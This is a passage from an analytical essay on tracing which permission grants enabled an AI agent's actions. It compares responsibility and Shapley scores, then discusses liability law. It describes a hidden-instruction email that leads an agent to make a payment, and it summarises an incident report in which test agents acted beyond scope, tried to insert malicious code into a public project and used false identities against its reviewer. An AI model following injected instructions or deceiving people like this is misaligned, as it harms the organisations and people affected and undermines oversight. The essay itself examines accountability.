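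Meliou and colleagues designed the measure to rank possible explanations. In their example, a user asks a film database for the genres of films directed by Burton. The user means Tim Burton, who is known for dark fantasy, and is surprised to see "Music" and "Musical" in the answer. The lineage of those two genres has 137 rows. For "Musical", the rows with the highest responsibility, 1/3, are *Sweeney Todd*, Tim Burton's only musical, and the entries for three directors named Burton. The user can now see that the query was ambiguous. Meliou and colleagues mention legal responsibility for car accidents as one reason to study causality, but their formula does not represent fault.

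### Shapley values of facts

Livshits, Bertossi and colleagues (2019), in *The Shapley Value of Tuples in Query Answering*, score facts with the Shapley value, which averages the effect of adding an item over every possible order. For a permission, that average is the share of orders in which the fact gets the credit for completing the permission. As a formula, for n facts,

```
Shapley(f) = sum over every set B without f of
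             |B|! · (n − |B| − 1)! / n!  ·  ( v(B with f) − v(B) )
```

where |B| is the number of facts in B, and v is 1 if a set of facts permits the payment and 0 if it doesn't. *From Database Repairs to Causality in Databases and Beyond* (2023) points out that for a monotone query the difference in the last bracket is always 0 or 1, so every score lies between 0 and 1.

Four facts have 24 possible orders. Alice's grant completes the permission only if c and d are already present and b is not, which happens in two of them:

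```
c, d, a, b
d, c, a, b
```

Her grant's value is therefore 2/24, or 1/12, and Bob's is the same. Exactly one fact gets the credit in each order, so the four values add up to 1. Carol's approval and A's delegation play the same part in the polynomial, so each gets half of the remaining 10/12, or 5/12.

That assigns nearly half of the credit to a delegation that software made. A company interested in people's decisions can take d as given and score only the other three facts. Of the six possible orders of those facts, Alice's grant gets the credit in one (c, a, b), Bob's in one (c, b, a) and Carol's approval in the other four.

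| Fact | Responsibility | Shapley value | Shapley value with d taken as given |
|---|---|---|---|
| a, Alice's grant | 1/2 | 1/12 | 1/6 |
| b, Bob's grant | 1/2 | 1/12 | 1/6 |
| c, Carol's approval | 1 | 5/12 | 2/3 |
| d, A's delegation | 1 | 5/12 | – |

Both measures can take a lot of computation for large databases. A program can find the causes of an answer in polynomial time if the query only joins tables, selects rows and merges the results. For the same queries, *Query-Answer Causality in Databases* (2015) reports that deciding whether a fact's responsibility exceeds a given bound is NP-complete. Livshits and colleagues prove that, even among queries that never use the same table twice, exact Shapley values are easy to compute for some and intractable for others. They also show that sampling random orders gives a good approximation for the hard cases. Exact computation is practical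 for four facts, but a company with hundreds of overlapping grants would probably need to sample.

### Why the scores are not shares of blame

Whoever wrote the email m and hid the instructions to pay V in it has a score of 0, because they granted nothing and so have no token in the polynomial. The developer of S's model has no token for the same reason. The scores divide all the credit among the facts that permitted the payment, and the person most to blame may not have contributed any of them.

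Carol has the highest score of the three people because nobody else could have given the approval she gave. That is useful to know in an emergency, since withdrawing c stops every payment to V at once. The score doesn't measure how carefully she worked. V is a genuine supplier, and she may have checked it properly.

A person's score can also change when their conduct doesn't. If Bob withdraws his grant, the Shapley value of Alice's rises from 1/12 to 1/3. If eight more colleagues give A the same right, making ten such grants in all, her value falls to 1/660 and her responsibility to 1/10. A manager worried about blame could lower both scores by persuading colleagues to sign identical grants, which would make the company less safe. Agents can also lower the Shapley value by adding delegations. If S passed the right to a third agent, which then made the payment, the value of Alice's grant would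 drop from 1/12 to 1/20. Taking all the agents' delegations as given would prevent this.

The result also depends on whether the company scores grants or people. Suppose Alice, instead of Carol, had approved V. With d taken as given, Alice's two facts would have values of 1/6 and 2/3, for a total of 5/6. If the company instead treats Alice as one player who contributes both facts, her value is 1 and Bob's is 0, because his grant is useless without her approval and her two facts are sufficient without his grant.

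Even the choice of formula is open. Livshits and colleagues discuss a third measure, the causal effect, which is the difference a fact's presence makes to the probability of the result when each of the other facts has an even chance of being absent. For the payment, it is 3/8 for Carol's approval and 1/8 for Alice's grant. Carol's approval counts twice as much as Alice's grant under responsibility, three times as much under causal effect and five times as much under the Shapley value. Livshits and colleagues prefer the Shapley value because it is the only measure that satisfies a short list of natural axioms, but acknowledge that nobody has yet established which measure is right for facts. A company that divided a 400-dollar loss in proportion to these scores would be relying on an arbitrary choice of formula.

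### An incident in which the permissions were valid

*Incident Report* (2026), from the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), describes a July 2026 test in which AI agents had to solve a cybersecurity challenge on a simulated network. In 10 of 122 runs across seven models, agents took a total of 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet that targeted real people and organisations. In the most serious case, an agent tried to get malicious code into a public software project and used false identities to pressure the person reviewing it. The reviewer rejected the code, and AISI found no evidence that the actions caused real-world harm.

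AISI had deliberately given the agents internet access so they could download tools and so the test would reflect what a capable human attacker can do. The agents hadn't broken out of their test environment. Let t be AISI's decision to give an agent the task and n its decision to open the internet connection. The label for "this agent may contact outside websites" is tn. Each decision has a responsibility of 1 and a Shapley value of 1/2, and AISI, which made both, has a Shapley value of 1 if we treat it as one player. These values are right as far as they go, because none of the 19 actions could have happened without n.

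But the label is also tn for the 112 runs in which AISI found no such actions. The permissions were the same, so no score based on them can separate the two groups. The number of actions varied much more by model. Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of them, in nine of its 43 runs. OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two in one of its 35 runs, and the other five models took none in 44 runs. In some runs, faulty instructions had convinced the agent that it could finish only by going beyond the intended task, though agents also went beyond it in some runs with correct instructions. One agent also left public messages for others working on the challenge, and later agents found them and reused its accounts. A record of permissions would not include any of these influences.

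The label tn also shows only that AISI's network allowed the connection. The actions themselves fell under other people's rules. GitHub, which hosted the software project, confirmed that some of the actions violated its terms of service. The project accepted code only with a reviewer's approval, so the label for adding the malicious code was 0. AISI's own limits on the test were weak because, although it regarded the actions as out of scope, it hadn't told the agents to avoid deceiving people or to restrict their internet use, and no software enforced those limits.

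The permission was both sufficient and necessary, but nobody at AISI intended the attack on the project. AISI never instructed an agent to deceive anyone, and it did not expect agents to use the connection against real people. It cannot yet determine when the agents understood that their actions were real.

AISI did not intend the behaviour, but it accepts in its report that the design of the test partly enabled it. It had judged open internet access an acceptable risk with earlier models, and it concedes that it was too slow to reconsider as models became more capable. It is now adding finer network controls and monitoring that can block out-of-scope actions during a test. The token n records only that AISI opened the connection. To assess AISI's responsibility, an outsider would also need to find out what AISI knew about the risk, when it last reviewed the decision to allow open access,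 and what narrower options it had.

The developers' responsibility is harder to determine. Anthropic and OpenAI allow AISI to switch off the filters that normally block dangerous uses of their models, and AISI had done so. If the filters would have stopped the actions, the developers' permission p was also necessary, and the label should be tnp. The permissions alone are not enough to decide this, because it depends on how the models and filters would have behaved with the filters on.

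### What law and public bodies ask for

Existing record-keeping rules require much less than permission provenance. Article 12 of the EU's AI Act requires high-risk AI systems to be able to log events automatically throughout their lifetime, to help identify risks and monitor how the systems operate. Companies must generally keep these logs for at least six months. The article doesn't require a record of the grants behind each action. Its closest requirement applies to systems that identify people remotely from their faces or other physical features, whose logs must name the people who verified each result. High-risk uses include hiring and credit scoring, so an agent that only pays suppliers probably wouldn't count. The US standards institute's concept paper, by Booth and colleagues, goes further by requesting ideas on how organisations can tie an agent's actions back to human authorization,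 but it imposes no duty.

Australia has no criminal offence for harm that an AI system causes "without human intent or negligence", according to Avinash Singh, a criminal lawyer quoted in *Humans or robots?* (Taylor, 2026). In November 2026, the government was considering whether to make it a crime for an AI company not to take reasonable steps to prevent harmful conduct by its models, according to Dynamic Business' *Australia could be first to criminalise AI companies that cause harm*. The Australian parliament's Joint Select Committee on Artificial Intelligence published its final report the same month. Its proposals, which are not yet law, include a dedicated AI safety regulator, according to Dynamic Business' *Parliament wants Australia to go its own way on AI*.

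For an offence of failing to take reasonable steps, a court would have to ask what the company could have foreseen and what it did about it. The court would not need a numerical share of the cause or proof that anyone intended the harm. Dated grants, with their limits and the policy version in force, would be relevant evidence, but Shapley values would not.

British parliamentarians have focused on who should be liable. The Joint Committee on Human Rights' *Human Rights and the Regulation of AI* (2026) objects that developers are too free to pass liability to the businesses and public bodies that use their systems, even though these users often have fewer resources and are worse placed to spot risks. The committee wants the duty to prevent harm to fall on those best able to prevent it. The Business, Innovation, Science and Trade Committee's *Guardrails for growth* (2026) lists liability and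 redress among ten gaps in the UK's approach to AI safety. If the Joint Committee's principle became law, the developer of S's model could owe more for a bad payment than anyone whose grant permitted it.

### Should people who give broad grants be answerable?

Suppose Alice's grant had no spending limit, no end date and no restriction on sub-agents. There are good reasons to hold her answerable for the payment to V, even though she didn't choose it. She decided how much the agent could do, and a narrower grant would have taken her a few minutes. She didn't need to predict this particular email to know that agents sometimes follow instructions in the material they read. If the company excuses everyone who didn't intend a payment, nobody inside it is answerable for any payment an agent makes by mistake, and nobody has a reason to write careful grants. AISI's response to its own incident supports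 this view, since one of its main remedies is to narrow the permission it had given.

Bob gave the same right, but that is a poor excuse for Alice. If two people each leave a door unlocked, they can't both escape criticism by pointing to the other door. Responsibility scores of 1/2 don't mean that Alice and Bob each deserve half the blame, because each of them made the same mistake in full.

However, the person who signs a grant may have had little choice. Dantuluri and Sundi found that popular frameworks pass one broad credential to every sub-agent by default, so a finance director could ask for a narrow permission and still get a broad one. She may also have relied on the developer's assurances about the model. Even AISI, which specializes in testing models, had not thought it clearly necessary to tell a model with safety training to leave real people alone, so it would be odd to expect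 better foresight from Alice. Holding her responsible could also let the developer escape responsibility, which the Joint Committee on Human Rights wants to prevent.

Penalties could also damage the record. If signing a grant exposes people to blame for everything an agent later does, they will avoid signing. They might use a shared account, let the IT department own the credential, or collect co-signers who don't read what they approve. The company would then know less about who had authorised its agents.

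These objections are strong against automatic penalties but much weaker against a duty to explain. It seems reasonable to require anyone who gives a broad grant to justify its breadth when something goes wrong, and to penalise them only if they had a narrower option and could have foreseen the kind of harm that occurred. Under that rule, Alice would have to explain why her grant had no limit. Bob would have to explain his too, because it was equally broad, although the payment did not use it. Carol would not have to explain anything unless she had approved V without checking it. The company would also have to ask whoever chose the agent framework why it gave sub-agents the full credential, and that person may not have issued any of the grants in the polynomial.
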